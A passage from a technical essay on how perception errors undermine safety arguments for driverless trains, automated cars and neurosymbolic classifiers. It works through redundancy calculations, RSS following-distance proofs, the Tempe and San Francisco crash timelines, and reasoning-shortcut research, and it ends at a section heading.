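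A proof of concept for clear-track detection avoids the problem of rejected stop signs. *New Methods for Safety Demonstrations* (Henon, 2025), a talk for the International Union of Railways, describes a neural network that proposes a path along the rails and a conventional program that checks the path with a second camera. The program looks for a rail on each side of the path, checks that the two are parallel and 1,435 millimeters apart, and calculates how far the clear track extends. If the check fails, the distance is 0 and the train has to stop, so a wrong rejection delays the train but doesn't make it less safe.

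The network was only about 90 percent accurate after training on 650 pictures from a train simulation game. The safety argument depends on the claim that only a clear track can look like two parallel lines at that spacing, not on the network's accuracy. I doubt that claim, because a suitcase lying between the rails could leave both rails in view, and a correct checker would then certify a path with an obstacle on it.

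### Two channels and the value of independence

In KI-LOK, a stop sign reaches the controller only if the detector finds it and the checker accepts it. If the detector misses 4 percent of stop signs and the checker rejects 19 percent of the rest, 22 percent of stop signs never reach the controller. By contrast, *Probabilistic Risk Assessment of an Obstacle Detection System* (Gleirscher, Haxthausen and Peleska, 2023) describes a design for slow driverless freight trains that reports an obstacle if either of two channels does. One channel uses a neural network, and the other preferably uses conventional image processing.

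Suppose each channel misses 4 percent of obstacles. If the misses are independent, both channels miss the same obstacle with probability 0.04 × 0.04 = 0.0016, or once in 625 cases. If the channels always miss the same obstacles, the probability remains 0.04, or once in 25 cases, and adding the second channel does not reduce the number of missed obstacles.

A rate of 0.0016 is still too high, so Gleirscher and colleagues use three such modules and brake the train whenever the modules disagree. They assume that an obstacle or degraded input occurs twice a day and aim for less than 10⁻⁷ dangerous misses per hour:

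all six channels independent: 2/24 × 0.0016³ ≈ 3.4 × 10⁻¹⁰ per hour
all six channels fail together: 2/24 × 0.04 ≈ 3.3 × 10⁻³ per hour

The first figure easily meets the target, while the second means about one dangerous miss every 12 days. Independence accounts for the entire difference, a factor of almost ten million.

To get the error rate of a single channel, Gleirscher and colleagues adapt the coupon collector's problem, which asks how many random draws it takes to see every type of coupon at least once. They divide the pictures that the network recognizes as obstacles into ℓ classes, with class i turning up with probability pᵢ. The expected number of draws from a picture database until every class has appeared is:

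E(X) = ∫₀^∞ (1 − ∏ᵢ (1 − e^(−pᵢx))) dx

They then add a hypothetical class of obstacles that the network can't recognize, and calculate how many draws would almost certainly include one. If that many draws include none, they conclude with the chosen confidence that the class doesn't exist. Strictly, this rules out only classes at least as common as the hypothetical one. Ruling out a class that makes up 1 in 10,000 pictures with 95 percent confidence takes about 30,000 independent draws, and no number of draws will reveal a kind of obstacle missing from the database.

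To test whether the channels are independent, they find which pixels were essential to each channel's answer and apply a chi-square test, a standard test for statistical association, to the two sets of pixels. If the test finds a dependence, they retrain the network or change its structure. But two channels can rely on different pixels and still fail on the same pictures, because some pictures are hard for any method.

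For example, suppose each channel misses 1 percent of obstacles in good light and 31 percent in poor light, and 10 percent of the pictures have poor light. The overall miss rate is again 4 percent. Even if the channels are independent within each kind of light, both miss an obstacle with probability 0.9 × 0.01² + 0.1 × 0.31² ≈ 0.0097, six times the figure for full independence. With all six channels, the rate becomes about 7 × 10⁻⁶ per hour, which is 70 times the target. Gleirscher and colleagues expect the sensors to detect fog, snow and sandstorms and stop the train, but ordinary dim light might not trigger a stop.

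Their model also includes only situations with an obstacle or degraded input, so it doesn't show how often false alarms would stop the train on a clear track. In KI-LOK, false alarms kept the unprotected train from moving. They also note that under the European railway standard EN 50129, redundancy counts as an argument only against random hardware faults, not against errors a network has learned.

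### Certification in 2025 and 2026

Railway standards still offer little help with learned components. Zeller and Schnitzer (2025), in *Assuring Safety of AI-based Systems*, report on safe.trAIn, a project that drew up an example safety case for a driverless regional train. They listed known weaknesses of machine learning and tried to show that each was under control. Existing methods were enough for many of them, including mislabeled data and overfitting. The project could not show that results on synthetic images carry over to real ones, or that the detector is reliable in rare situations, and it did not address the network's uncertainty. *Building Trust in Artificial Intelligence* (2026) concludes that nobody can establish compliance until there are norms for AI in railways. *Railway Artificial Intelligence Learning Benchmark (RAIL-BENCH)* (2026) introduces the first benchmark suite for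 railway perception, so shared measurements of error are also new.

Trials on real track have nevertheless begun. *Results of automatically stabling a train* (Braakman, Lammers and colleagues, 2026) describes 49 runs of a Dutch passenger train in driverless mode between June and September 2025. The train ran between Hengelo and Enschede and in the adjacent yards, with a safety driver but no passengers on board. It stopped for the buffer stops and other trains it encountered.

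Its software handles missing information more cautiously than the KI-LOK controller. If the perception system stops delivering results, the train brakes, and the software continues to treat a reported obstacle as present for some time after it disappears from view. Neither precaution helps if the network never detects the obstacle. The train was supposed to use several kinds of sensor and both learned and conventional algorithms, but only a stereo camera with one neural network was active in the moving tests, partly because the unit with the laser scanner was unreliable. The trial therefore didn't test the redundancy on which the calculation by Gleirscher and colleagues depends.

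In stationary daytime tests, the system detected people at 50 to 70 meters, which a train at the line's limit of 125 kilometers per hour covers in about two seconds. The 49 driverless runs lasted 9 hours and 45 minutes in total. Even with no dangerous failures, they would only support a failure rate below about 0.3 per hour with 95 percent confidence. Demonstrating a rate of 10⁻⁷ per hour through test runs alone would take about 30 million hours.

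## Automated driving: proved driving rules and misclassified events

No set of rules can guarantee that an automated car will never be in a collision, because other drivers can always run into it. In *On a Formal Model of Safe and Scalable Self-driving Cars*, Shalev-Shwartz, Shammah and Shashua (2017) give the example of a car surrounded by other cars on a highway. They therefore aim to prove only that the car never causes a collision. They developed their rules, called Responsibility-Sensitive Safety (RSS), at Mobileye, a maker of driver-assistance systems.

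Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues wanted a proof because testing would take too long. Human drivers have about one fatal accident per million hours, and the researchers think the public will expect machines to be a thousand times safer. Showing this by test driving would take about a billion hours, or 30 billion miles, and the testing would have to start over after every change to the planning software.

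### A safe following distance

RSS turns five common-sense rules into formulas, starting with the rule not to hit the car in front. Suppose a rear car with speed v_r follows a lead car with speed v_f. In the worst case, the lead car suddenly brakes as hard as it can, while the rear car keeps accelerating for a response time ρ before it brakes. The smallest safe gap is then:

d_min = v_r·ρ + ½·a·ρ² + (v_r + a·ρ)² / (2·b_r) − v_f² / (2·b_f)

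Here a is the rear car's greatest acceleration during the response time, b_r is the weakest braking it will use afterwards, and b_f is the hardest braking expected from the lead car. If the result is negative, the safe gap is 0.

For example, let both cars drive at 20 meters per second (about 45 miles per hour), with ρ = 0.5 seconds, a = 2, b_r = 4 and b_f = 8 m/s²:

d_min = 10 + 0.25 + 55.125 − 25 ≈ 40.4 meters

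The rear car needs 65.4 meters to stop and the lead car needs 25, so if they start 40.4 meters apart, they stop with no gap between them.

RSS calls a situation dangerous when the gap is smaller than d_min. The rear car must then give a "proper response". For ρ seconds it may accelerate by at most a, and after that it must brake by at least b_r until the gap is safe again or it has stopped. A stopped car may not start in a dangerous situation. The proof that the rear car never hits the lead car is an induction over time:

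1. Before the rear car first sets off, it cannot have hit anyone, and it sets off only when the gap is safe.
2. While the gap is safe there is no collision, because the gap has to become unsafe before it can reach zero.
3. At the moment when the gap becomes unsafe, it is still as large as d_min, which is enough for the proper response to prevent a collision. The response ends with a safe gap or with the rear car at a standstill.
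4. From a safe gap, step 2 applies again. From a standstill, the car waits until the gap is safe, and then step 2 applies.

If there are several other cars, the car calculates a separate acceleration limit for each and obeys the strictest. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues extend the argument to lane changes, junctions, pedestrians and blocked views, and conclude that there would be no collisions if everyone followed the rules. *Slow Down, Move Over* (2023) gives a machine-checked proof for motion along the lane, using the theorem prover KeYmaera X. It also derives Python code from the proved model in steps that preserve safety.

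### If the lead car is missing or its speed is wrong

The calculation uses the list of objects that perception supplies. If the lead car is missing from that list, there is no gap to calculate and no limit to obey, so the automated car can accelerate into the lead car without breaking a rule. The formula "always (reported gap too small → proper response)" is still true, because it describes only the symbols that perception reports and not the actual distance between the cars.

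A wrong speed can be just as harmful. Suppose the lead car has stopped but perception reports that it is moving at 20 meters per second. The safe gap is 65.4 meters, but the automated car doesn't respond until the gap is 40.4 meters. Even if it then brakes at 4 m/s² all the way, it hits the stopped car at about 14 meters per second. A smaller error, such as reporting the lead car's speed as 22 instead of 20 meters per second, shortens the required gap by only about 5 meters.

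How much a position error matters depends on its direction. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues consider a car driving at 30 meters per second toward a stopped vehicle 150 meters ahead. If the vehicle is in the car's lane, the car must immediately brake at 3 m/s², but if the vehicle is at the side of the road, the car doesn't need to brake hard. The two positions may be only 5 meters apart, about 3 percent of the distance to the vehicle. The researchers therefore recommend measuring sideways position in lane widths, so that an error large enough to put a vehicle in the wrong lane also counts as large in the statistics.

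### Three sensing systems and a vote

For safety, Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues count only errors that change whether a situation appears dangerous. These are misses, which make a dangerous situation look safe, and ghosts, which make a safe situation look dangerous and can make the car brake hard for no reason when another car is close behind. The target is at most one such error per billion hours.

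They propose three sensing systems that use different technologies, such as cameras, radar and lidar (which measures distances with laser light). Each system decides whether the situation is dangerous, and the majority wins. Suppose each system has a probability of at most p of a miss and at most p of a ghost, and any two make the same kind of error together at most c times as often as they would by chance. Then:

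P(miss or ghost after the vote) ≤ 6·c·p²

With p = 10⁻⁵ per hour and c = 1, the bound is 6 × 10⁻¹⁰, which meets the target. Testing each system separately then takes on the order of 100,000 hours of recorded driving instead of a billion.

As in the calculation by Gleirscher and colleagues for freight trains, the result depends almost entirely on how independently the systems fail. With these numbers, the bound exceeds the target once c is above about 1.7. If the three systems always failed together, the vote would not help and the error rate would be at least 10,000 times the target. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues argue that the systems fail for different reasons. Bad weather affects cameras but not radar, while irrelevant metal objects affect radar but not cameras. Fog affects both cameras and lidar, but cameras tend to miss objects in fog and lidar tends to report objects that aren't there.

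This is plausible, but it doesn't establish that c is below 1.7. Measuring c directly would require counting how often two systems fail together, which at c = 1 happens once in 10 billion hours. That would take even longer than the test the design is meant to avoid. Using recordings from human drivers also assumes that the automated car's driving hardly changes what its sensors encounter. Scarbro and colleagues could not assume this for their shield. Researchers later proposed PURSS, a version of RSS for uncertain perception, which the introduction *Responsibility-Sensitive Safety* (2022) cites.

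### Objections to the rules

Even with perfect perception, the guarantee depends on numbers the car cannot know, such as how hard the car in front can brake. If that car brakes harder than the assumed limit b_f, the proof no longer applies. Setting b_f to infinity treats every car ahead as stationary and raises the required gap in the example to 65.4 meters, too much for normal traffic. The gap depends mostly on the assumed braking rates. If both cars were assumed to brake at 8 m/s², it would be only 12.8 meters. Shalev-Shwartz and colleagues want regulators to set these values. That would help assign blame for a collision, but it wouldn't change how hard cars actually brake.

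*Algorithmic Ethics* (2021) objects that RSS states its rules as equations of motion rather than in formal logic, so nobody can derive their logical consequences. It adds a logic of obligation and permission that omits the equations of motion. The machine-checked proof covers motion, but only along the lane, and doesn't include obligation and permission.

RSS also has no rules for what a car should do after a collision, which was the critical question in one of the two accidents below. The accidents show how a wrong symbol can lead to a harmful action. They do not refute a proof, because nobody had formally verified either automated car.

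### Tempe, 2018: a pedestrian whose label kept changing

On the evening of March 18, 2018, an Uber test car hit and killed a woman who was pushing a bicycle across a street in Tempe, Arizona, away from any crosswalk. The car was driving itself at about 45 miles per hour, with a human operator behind the wheel. The US National Transportation Safety Board (NTSB) investigated the crash. The NTSB's *Collision Between Vehicle Controlled by Developmental Automated Driving System and Pedestrian* (2019) lists the labels and predictions that the software recorded:

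| Seconds before impact | Label | Predicted path |
|---|---|---|
| 5.6 | vehicle | none |
| 5.2 | other | stays in place |
| 4.2 | vehicle | stays in place |
| 3.9 | vehicle | along the lane next to the car's |
| 3.8 to 2.7 | alternates between vehicle and other | alternates between the two paths above |
| 2.6 | bicycle | stays in place |
| 2.5 | bicycle | along the lane next to the car's |
| 1.5 | other | stays in place, partly in the car's lane |
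| 1.2 | bicycle | in the car's lane |

The software never labeled the woman as a pedestrian, and two rules turned the wrong labels into wrong predictions. The first rule assigned goals to objects based on their labels. The software normally predicted that vehicles and bicycles in a traffic lane would continue along it, but it gave objects labeled "other" no goal and treated them as stationary. The second rule discarded an object's earlier positions whenever its label changed, so after each new label the software predicted the woman's path as if it had just detected her, even though the sensors had followed her toward the car's path for more than four seconds.

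Keeping the history might not have been enough, because the software would still have assumed that a bicycle follows its lane. With the label "pedestrian", it could have predicted a path across the road, but only if it had kept that label long enough to measure her speed. Checking the code against its specification would not have revealed the problem, because the designers intended the software to discard the history.

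A correct prediction 2.5 seconds before impact would probably have prevented the crash. The software could brake at up to 7 m/s² and increase its braking by up to 5 m/s² each second. Within those limits, the car needed about 42 meters to stop and was still about 48 meters away. When the software detected the danger, 1.2 seconds before impact, the car was about 22 meters away, too close to stop.

Two further rules then delayed the braking. In an emergency, the software waited one second before it braked, because Uber was concerned about false alarms. After that second, it was allowed to brake hard only if this could still prevent the collision. Hard braking could not, so the software sounded an alert and began to slow the car gradually 0.2 seconds before impact. The car was still traveling at 39 miles per hour just before it hit her.

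Uber had also disabled the car's factory-installed emergency braking while its own software was driving. Volvo, the car's manufacturer, simulated 20 variations of the woman's movements, assuming ideal sensors, and found that this system would have avoided the collision in 17 and reduced the impact speed to below 10 miles per hour in the other three.

The NTSB concluded that the probable cause was the operator's failure to monitor the road because she was looking at her phone. It listed Uber's poor risk assessment and weak supervision of operators among the contributing factors. Uber later changed the software to keep an object's history when its label changes, and to brake as hard as allowed even when this only reduces the impact. According to Fortune (2019), Uber told the NTSB that the new software would have started braking more than four seconds before impact. This is Uber's own estimate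 for a scene it had already studied in detail.

### San Francisco, 2023: the wrong type of collision

On October 2, 2023, a human-driven Nissan in San Francisco hit a woman who was crossing against the signal and threw her in front of a driverless taxi owned by Cruise, a General Motors subsidiary. The taxi ran her over, stopped, and then dragged her about 20 feet while pulling over, but she survived.

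The public evidence comes from two investigations that the companies commissioned. The law firm Quinn Emanuel wrote the report that Cruise (2024) filed with a California regulator, which covers the company's dealings with officials and leaves out vehicle safety. The engineering consultancy Exponent analyzed the technical causes. Koopman (2024), in *Anatomy of a Robotaxi Crash*, combines the two into one timeline:

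| Seconds from impact | Event |
|---|---|
| −4.8 | The predicted paths of the woman and the Nissan would allow a collision, but the software doesn't consider one |
| −2.9 | The Nissan hits her |
| −2.0 | The software loses track of her and from then on detects her only intermittently |
| −0.78 | She enters the taxi's lane, 21.5 feet ahead |
| −0.3 | The software labels her as a pedestrian for the last time |
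| −0.25 | The software orders braking and steering |
| 0 | The taxi hits her at 18.6 miles per hour, and the software classifies this as a side impact |
| 0.23 | The left front wheel runs over her |
| 1.78 | The taxi stops |
| 1.83 | It starts to pull over, with the woman underneath |
| 5.8 | Wheel slip causes the software to slow the taxi down |
| 8.8 | The taxi stops for good |

The wrong symbol was "side impact", and the rule for it was to pull over. That rule makes sense after a minor collision with another car, since a stopped taxi blocks traffic and someone may run into it. According to Carrier Management (2024), Exponent concluded that the taxi drove on instead of making an emergency stop because its software was wrong about where the woman was, which part of the taxi had hit her, and where the taxi itself was.

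The software classified the collision using its tracking data from just before the impact, when the taxi's body largely hid the woman from its lidar. A camera on the left side showed her feet and lower legs the whole time. The software briefly detected her legs but neither classified nor tracked them.

The braking before the impact was more robust because it didn't need a correct label. The software detected "occupied space" ahead and braked in case it was a person. But after the impact, the software let the taxi move unless it had evidence that someone was in danger. Under the principle of fail-safe defaults, the taxi would have stayed stopped until something established that moving was safe. Koopman argues that it should at least have waited for approval from the remote assistance team. The team was connected within five seconds, but the taxi was already pulling over by then.

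Exponent also found that the taxi could have avoided the woman if it had braked as soon as she entered its lane. The order to brake came 0.53 seconds later, close to the 0.5-second response time in the RSS example above. Under RSS, the taxi would therefore probably not be to blame for the first impact, but the rule would not have protected the woman. Exponent found no hardware or software faults, so this accident, too, came from a design that worked as intended.

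### Which label errors matter

As in the door example, an overall accuracy figure doesn't separate harmless perception errors from dangerous ones. The Caltech thesis chapter *Evaluating Perception for System-Level Task Requirements* proposes statistics that do, building on papers by Badithela, Wongpiromsarn and Murray from 2021 and 2023.

Its example is a car that approaches a crosswalk. The car must stop just before the crosswalk if a pedestrian is there, and must not stop otherwise. As in the TaxiNet analysis, a confusion matrix supplies the error probabilities for a Markov chain. The matrix comes from running a lidar-based detector on nuScenes, a public collection of recorded city driving:

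| The detector reports | Actual pedestrians | Actual obstacles |
|---|---|---|
| pedestrian | 14,884 | 751 |
| obstacle | 650 | 48,693 |
| nothing | 7,966 | 14,921 |

The most common error in this table, missing an obstacle, is harmless in this simplified example because the car has to drive on whether the crosswalk is empty or contains an obstacle. The 8,616 errors in the pedestrian column are the dangerous ones, because each makes the car drive on when it should stop. Tuning the detector to find as many pedestrians as possible isn't always best, since that also produces more false reports, and the requirement forbids stopping for those.

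The statistics also depend on what one counts. If three pedestrians are standing together, the car only needs to detect that someone is there, so Badithela and colleagues count whether the detector gets the statement "there is a pedestrian" right. Within 10 meters, the detector finds 64 percent of individual pedestrians. When the only labeled objects at that distance are pedestrians, it reports pedestrians and nothing else in 72 percent of cases. But this figure can overstate the detector's performance, because finding a pedestrian behind the car counts as a success even if the detector misses one in front. When they evaluate the statement separately for areas about as wide as a car, the figure drops to 65 percent.

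They also work backwards from a safety requirement to the detector. In one example, the car must handle a pedestrian correctly with probability at least 0.99 × (1 − 0.1d), where d is the distance to the crosswalk, between 1 and 10 units. The detector must then recognize pedestrians at a rate of at least:

1.02 − 0.063d, and never less than 0.6

At a distance of 1 unit, the detector must recognize about 96 percent of pedestrians to guarantee correct behavior 89 percent of the time. The real detector also falls far short of what people usually expect of such systems, which is a failure probability between one in a million and one in a billion.

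Badithela and colleagues assume that only the car moves and that the detector locates objects perfectly. They also evaluate each moment separately, and expect better results from a system that tracks objects over time, because a single missed detection would matter less. But the Tempe crash shows that this depends on how the tracking works. Suppose a prediction requires five correct labels in a row, and each label is independently correct with probability 0.8. The software then gets all five only 33 percent of the time. If a system discards an object's history after every relabeling, its evaluation therefore needs to measure how often labels change as well as how often they are wrong.

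### Checking symbols against each other

Software can also look for perception errors by checking whether its symbols are consistent. In *NeuroStrata*, Zheng, Li and colleagues (2025) propose a driving system whose top layer describes the scene as objects and relations, such as "pedestrian crossing road", and checks the description against formal rules. So far they have tested only the use of such rules to train a network that describes videos.

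One of their example rules is that pedestrians and vehicles must not overlap in space. In San Francisco the woman was under the taxi, so a correct description of the scene would have violated it. The rule could have prevented the dragging if the software had treated the violation as a reason to stay stopped. But if the software had treated it as a perception error and removed her from its description of the scene, applying the rule would have hidden the emergency.

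## Neurosymbolic classifiers: symbols that do not mean what their names say

A neurosymbolic predictor is a classifier in two parts. A neural network turns an image into symbols, which researchers in this field call concepts, and fixed logical rules derive the answer from them. In a common driving example, the concepts are "red light" and "pedestrian", the answer is "stop" or "go", and the rule is:

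stop ⇔ red light or pedestrian

The design resembles that of the robot at the door, but the training is usually different. The KI-LOK researchers trained their sign detector on pictures in which the signs were labelled. Developers of neurosymbolic predictors mostly use images labelled only with the final answer, because labelling every concept in every image is expensive. The network then has to learn the concepts from those answers and the rules. *Symbol Grounding in Neuro-Symbolic AI* (Marconato, Morettin and colleagues, 2025) surveys how this goes wrong.

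### What the rules guarantee

The network gives each concept a probability. DeepProbLog, a well-known system of this kind, then computes the probability of an answer y by adding up the combinations of concepts c that lead to it:

P(y | image) = Σ P(c | image), summed over every c from which the rules derive y

Suppose the network gives "red light" a probability of 0.9 and "pedestrian" 0.2, and treats them as independent. The output is "go" only when neither is present, which has probability 0.1 × 0.8 = 0.08, so the probability of "stop" is 0.92.

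The classifier assigns probability zero to any combination of concepts and answer that breaks the rules. This guarantee holds for every image, including kinds absent from training, and for every network, even an untrained one. It is a property of the symbols and requires no assumption about perception.

The symbols that an engineer reads off may not match the classifier's answer. If a car must stop when either of two independent concepts is present, and each has probability 0.4, the most likely combination is that neither is present. But the probability of "stop" is 1 − 0.6 × 0.6 = 0.64, so the car stops even though the symbols show no reason to.

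Some systems guarantee less. Semantic Loss, for example, penalizes a network for breaking the rules during training but doesn't enforce them afterwards, so the network's answers on new images can violate them.

### A wrong assignment that fits every sum

MNIST-Half is a small test task with handwritten digits from 0 to 4. One network reads each digit separately, and the rule adds the two results. The training data contain only four sums. A network that reads 2 as 4, 3 as 1 and 4 as 2 gets all of them right:

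| Handwritten digits | Correct sum | What the network reads | Its answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 and 0 | 0 | 0 + 0 | 0 |
| 0 and 1 | 1 | 0 + 1 | 1 |
| 2 and 3 | 5 | 4 + 1 | 5 |
| 2 and 4 | 6 | 4 + 2 | 6 |
| 3 and 4 (not in training) | 7 | 1 + 2 | 3 |

On the new sum the answer is wrong, although the system still obeys the rule, since 1 + 2 is 3.

Marconato, Vergari and colleagues (2023), in *Not All Neuro-Symbolic Concepts Are Created Equal*, define a reasoning shortcut as a set of learned concepts that fits the training answers as well as possible but doesn't match the actual concepts. They also show how to count shortcuts. Let α be an assignment of reported concepts to actual ones, and let β be the rule that derives the answer. An assignment fits the training data if:

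β(α(g)) = β(g) for every combination g of actual concepts in the training data

Only one of the assignments that fit the training data is correct, and the others are shortcuts. In MNIST-Half, the first two sums force the network to read 0 and 1 correctly. If it reads 2 as s, it must read 3 as 5 − s and 4 as 6 − s, and all three values lie between 0 and 4 only if s is 2, 3 or 4. So three assignments fit, and two of them are shortcuts. More pictures of the same four sums would not rule out either shortcut, but adding 0 + 2 = 2 to the training data would rule out both.

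### Pedestrians reported as red lights

In the driving example, shortcuts remain even with a complete training set. The classifier must label an image with neither a red light nor a pedestrian as "neither", because only that label leads to "go". But it can label each of the other three situations as any of the three combinations that lead to "stop". So 3³ = 27 assignments fit all the data, and 26 of them are wrong.

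One of the 26 swaps the two concepts. Marconato, Vergari and colleagues consider what happens if someone reuses such a network in an autonomous ambulance, which may ignore red lights in an emergency:

| In the image | Reported concepts | Action under the ordinary rule | Action in an emergency | Correct action in an emergency |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| neither | neither | go | go | go |
| red light | pedestrian | stop | stop | go |
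| pedestrian | red light | stop | go | stop |
| both | both | stop | stop | stop |

The car always acts correctly under the ordinary rule, so no test of its actions could reveal the swap. But when the ambulance follows the new rule, it drives at pedestrians, even though that rule is correct and correctly implemented.

More pictures can correct a correctly trained detector's occasional errors if those errors are independent, but they can't correct the swapped network, which gets every lone pedestrian wrong. A guard that rejects uncertain outputs wouldn't help much either, because these predictors tend to be very confident about wrongly learned concepts, according to Marconato, Morettin and colleagues.

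A confusion matrix like TaxiNet's would reveal the swap, but it requires images with labelled concepts. Without such labels, developers can train several networks and compare their concepts. If the networks all answer correctly but disagree about the concepts, at least one has learned a shortcut. Agreement is weaker evidence, because they may all have learned the same shortcut.

### Right answers from wrong concepts

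Marconato, Vergari and colleagues tested how often shortcuts occur when the training set contains every combination of digits. They trained three kinds of system to add the digits shown in two images and kept only models that fitted the data almost perfectly. Between 83 and 100 percent of these models had learned a shortcut when one network processed both images together, but none had when the network had to process each image separately.

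Separate processing also removed all shortcuts from a task in which the answer was the parity of three bits, but with two bits a shortcut would survive. Swapping 0 and 1 in every bit changes the parity of three bits but not of two, so a network that misread both bits this way would still answer correctly. In road scenes, separate processing requires marking where each object is.

It also isn't enough when combinations are missing from the data. In MNIST-EvenOdd, training covers only 16 of the 100 possible digit pairs, 8 with two even digits and 8 with two odd ones. The next table gives F1 scores, which combine misses and false reports into a number from 0 to 100. All the networks processed each digit separately. Logic Tensor Networks uses degrees of truth instead of probabilities.

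| Added to training | DeepProbLog: sums | DeepProbLog: digits | Logic Tensor Networks: sums | Logic Tensor Networks: digits |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| nothing | 85.1 | 0.1 | 98.1 | 0.3 |
| reconstruction | 79.8 | 0.1 | 76.3 | 0.0 |
| spread | 98.1 | 0.1 | 81.9 | 53.9 |
| concept labels | 84.9 | 0.1 | 98.1 | 0.2 |
| spread and concept labels | 91.9 | 88.0 | 98.2 | 98.6 |
| all three | 95.4 | 96.2 | 98.1 | 98.5 |

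Random guessing would get about 10% of the digits right, so a score near zero can only come from a systematic mix-up. In these cases, the network gets most sums right while misreading almost every digit.

"Reconstruction" requires a second network to redraw the image from the concepts and some information about handwriting style. This prevents the first network from merging two digits into one symbol but still lets it swap their symbols. "Spread" rewards the network for using all symbols equally often. The remedies worked only in combination. The concept labels, which covered only some of the concepts, barely helped either system on their own.

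On real driving scenes the results were less clear-cut. BDD-OIA is a collection of dashcam images with 21 concepts and four possible actions, for which DeepProbLog achieved these F1 scores:

| Added to training | Actions | Concepts |
|---|---|---|
| nothing | 71.4 | 39.4 |
| spread | 72.1 | 48.1 |
| concept labels | 68.2 | 60.5 |
| spread and concept labels | 68.3 | 61.7 |

Concept labels raised the concept score by 21 points and lowered the action score by about 3. The concept score was still far below 100, partly because many images of left turns had wrong labels. All four versions obeyed the traffic rules by construction but still chose wrong actions in many scenes.

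Labelling also takes a lot of work. In the worst case, ruling out every shortcut requires labels for every combination of concepts, and 21 yes-or-no concepts have about 2.1 million combinations before the rules exclude any. The method in *Right for the Right Reasons* (Andolfi and Giunchiglia, 2025) needs far fewer labels because it assigns concepts by similarity to a few labelled examples. With one example per concept, DeepProbLog's concept score rose from 4 to 96 on MNIST-EvenOdd and from 25 to 94 on a visual logic task. But the survey by Marconato, Morettin and colleagues does not list this method or full concept labels as removing all shortcuts on BDD-OIA.

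Another remedy is to train the same concepts on two tasks. When Marconato, Vergari and colleagues trained DeepProbLog on both the sum and the product of two digits, its digit score was 99.8, up from 0 with sums alone and 37.6 with products alone. The choice of examples still matters. Contrary to the survey's claim, the sums and products of just two pairs, 4 with 5 and 3 with 2, allow more than one assignment, because exchanging 4 and 5 changes neither their sum nor their product.

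### Satisfying a rule without learning the concept

A classifier can take an even simpler shortcut with rules of the form "if A, then B" by never reporting A. Takemura and Inoue (2026) demonstrated this in *Differentiable Logic Programming to Mitigate Reasoning Shortcuts in Neurosymbolic Systems* by removing all labels for the digit 6 and supplying a rule instead. The rule was that if an image looks like a 9 after a half turn, the original image is a 6.

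A network trained with Semantic Loss satisfied the rule by never answering "9" on the turned images, but it recognized none of the sixes. Takemura and Inoue's own method, which ties each network output to one logical statement, recognized 92 percent of them.

### Checking the rules before training

Developers can look for shortcuts before they train anything, because shortcuts depend largely on the rules and the training combinations. Takemura, Inoue and Nishino (2026), in *Constraint-Based Analysis of Reasoning Shortcuts in Neurosymbolic Learning*, turn the question into a puzzle for a logic solver:

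1. List the actual concepts and the symbols that the network may assign to them.
2. Write every rule and training answer as a constraint, such as "the symbols for 2 and 3 add up to 5".
3. Check that the intended assignment satisfies all the constraints, then exclude it.
4. Search for any other assignment that satisfies them. If there is none, the task has no shortcuts.

For MNIST-Half, the solver finds the two shortcuts counted above. Both use one symbol for two different digits, so requiring a separate symbol for each digit removes them.

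Testing only whether two symbols can be swapped can miss other relabelings that satisfy every constraint. Suppose the symbols are 0, 1 and 2, and the second and third outputs must each be one more than the output before, with 0 following 2. Swapping any two symbols breaks a constraint, but replacing every symbol with the next one doesn't.

Takemura and colleagues prove that deciding whether a task is free of shortcuts is coNP-complete. A shortcut is easy to confirm, but every known method for showing that none exists can take exponentially long in the worst case. Counting the shortcuts is harder still (#P-complete). In practice, the searches took about half a second or less on eight tasks from *A Neuro-Symbolic Benchmark Suite for Concept Quality and Reasoning Shortcuts* (Bortolotti, Marconato and colleagues, 2024). They were capped at 10,000 solutions, and the search on BDD-OIA reached that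 cap.

A second algorithm repairs a task by fixing the meaning of one concept at a time, which amounts to supplying concept labels. BDD-OIA needed 21 such repairs for its 21 concepts, so the rules saved no labelling. On another driving task with 21 outputs, the algorithm failed to remove all shortcuts within 100 rounds. Takemura and colleagues attribute this to weak constraints, but that is hard to reconcile with the algorithm, which never fixes the same output twice and so should finish within 21 rounds.

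For the driving tasks, the constraints came from two to eight invented examples instead of the full training set. Extra constraints can only remove shortcuts, so a count of zero shortcuts is conclusive, but a high count may be an overestimate.

The check applies only to systems with explicit rules, and it assumes that the network always assigns the same symbol to a given actual concept. So it would not detect a network that recognizes a pedestrian only next to a red light, although that is one of the 26 shortcuts in the driving example.

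It also does not show whether training will succeed. With 0 + 2 = 2 added, MNIST-Half has no shortcuts, yet in Takemura and Inoue's experiments DeepProbLog read only 0.2 percent of the digits correctly, while another system, NeurASP, reached 97 percent. A network that misreads nearly every digit in this version must also get many training sums wrong, so this failure is visible in the answers.

### Proofs about small changes to an image

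Other proofs include the network itself. Manginas, Manginas and colleagues (2025), in *A Scalable Approach to Probabilistic Neuro-Symbolic Verification*, prove robustness, meaning that small changes to an image don't change the result. In their driving test, one network detects red lights and cars in front, and another chooses between braking and accelerating. The rules require braking for either hazard. Let b, a, r and c be the probabilities of "brake", "accelerate", "red light" and "car in front". The probability that the outputs obey the rules is:

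P = b + a · (1 − r) · (1 − c)

This formula uses only addition, subtraction and multiplication, so Manginas and colleagues can attach it to the two networks like another layer. They then allow every pixel value to change by up to ε and carry the resulting intervals through the whole computation. An image counts as robust if the lower bound on P is above 0.5.

Suppose the intervals are 0.6 to 0.9 for b, 0.1 to 0.4 for a, 0.3 to 0.4 for r and 0.1 to 0.2 for c. The lower bound is 0.6 + 0.1 × 0.6 × 0.8 = 0.648, so the image passes. The upper bound is 0.9 + 0.4 × 0.7 × 0.9 = 1.152, which is impossible for a probability. It exceeds 1 because the method does not use the fact that a and b always add up to 1. With that constraint, P lies between 0.792 and 0.963. The intervals always contain the true range, so a pass is a proof, but a failure may only mean that the intervals are too wide.

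Computing the exact range can require trying all 2ⁿ combinations of upper and lower limits for n outputs. The interval method took about 0.09 seconds per image. It proved 96.8 percent of the test images robust for ε = 0.00001 and 82.6 percent for 0.0001, but only 6.2 percent for 0.0005 and none for 0.001. If pixel values run from 0 to 1, as they usually do, one brightness step in an ordinary digital image is about 0.004. The proofs would then cover only changes too small for the camera to record, not rain or glare.

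The property also checks whether the two networks' outputs are consistent with each other, not whether they match the road. If one network misses a red light and the other accelerates, the outputs obey the rules and the image can count as robust. A detector that swaps "red light" and "car in front" also passes, because the two are interchangeable in the rule.

### Specifications that contain networks

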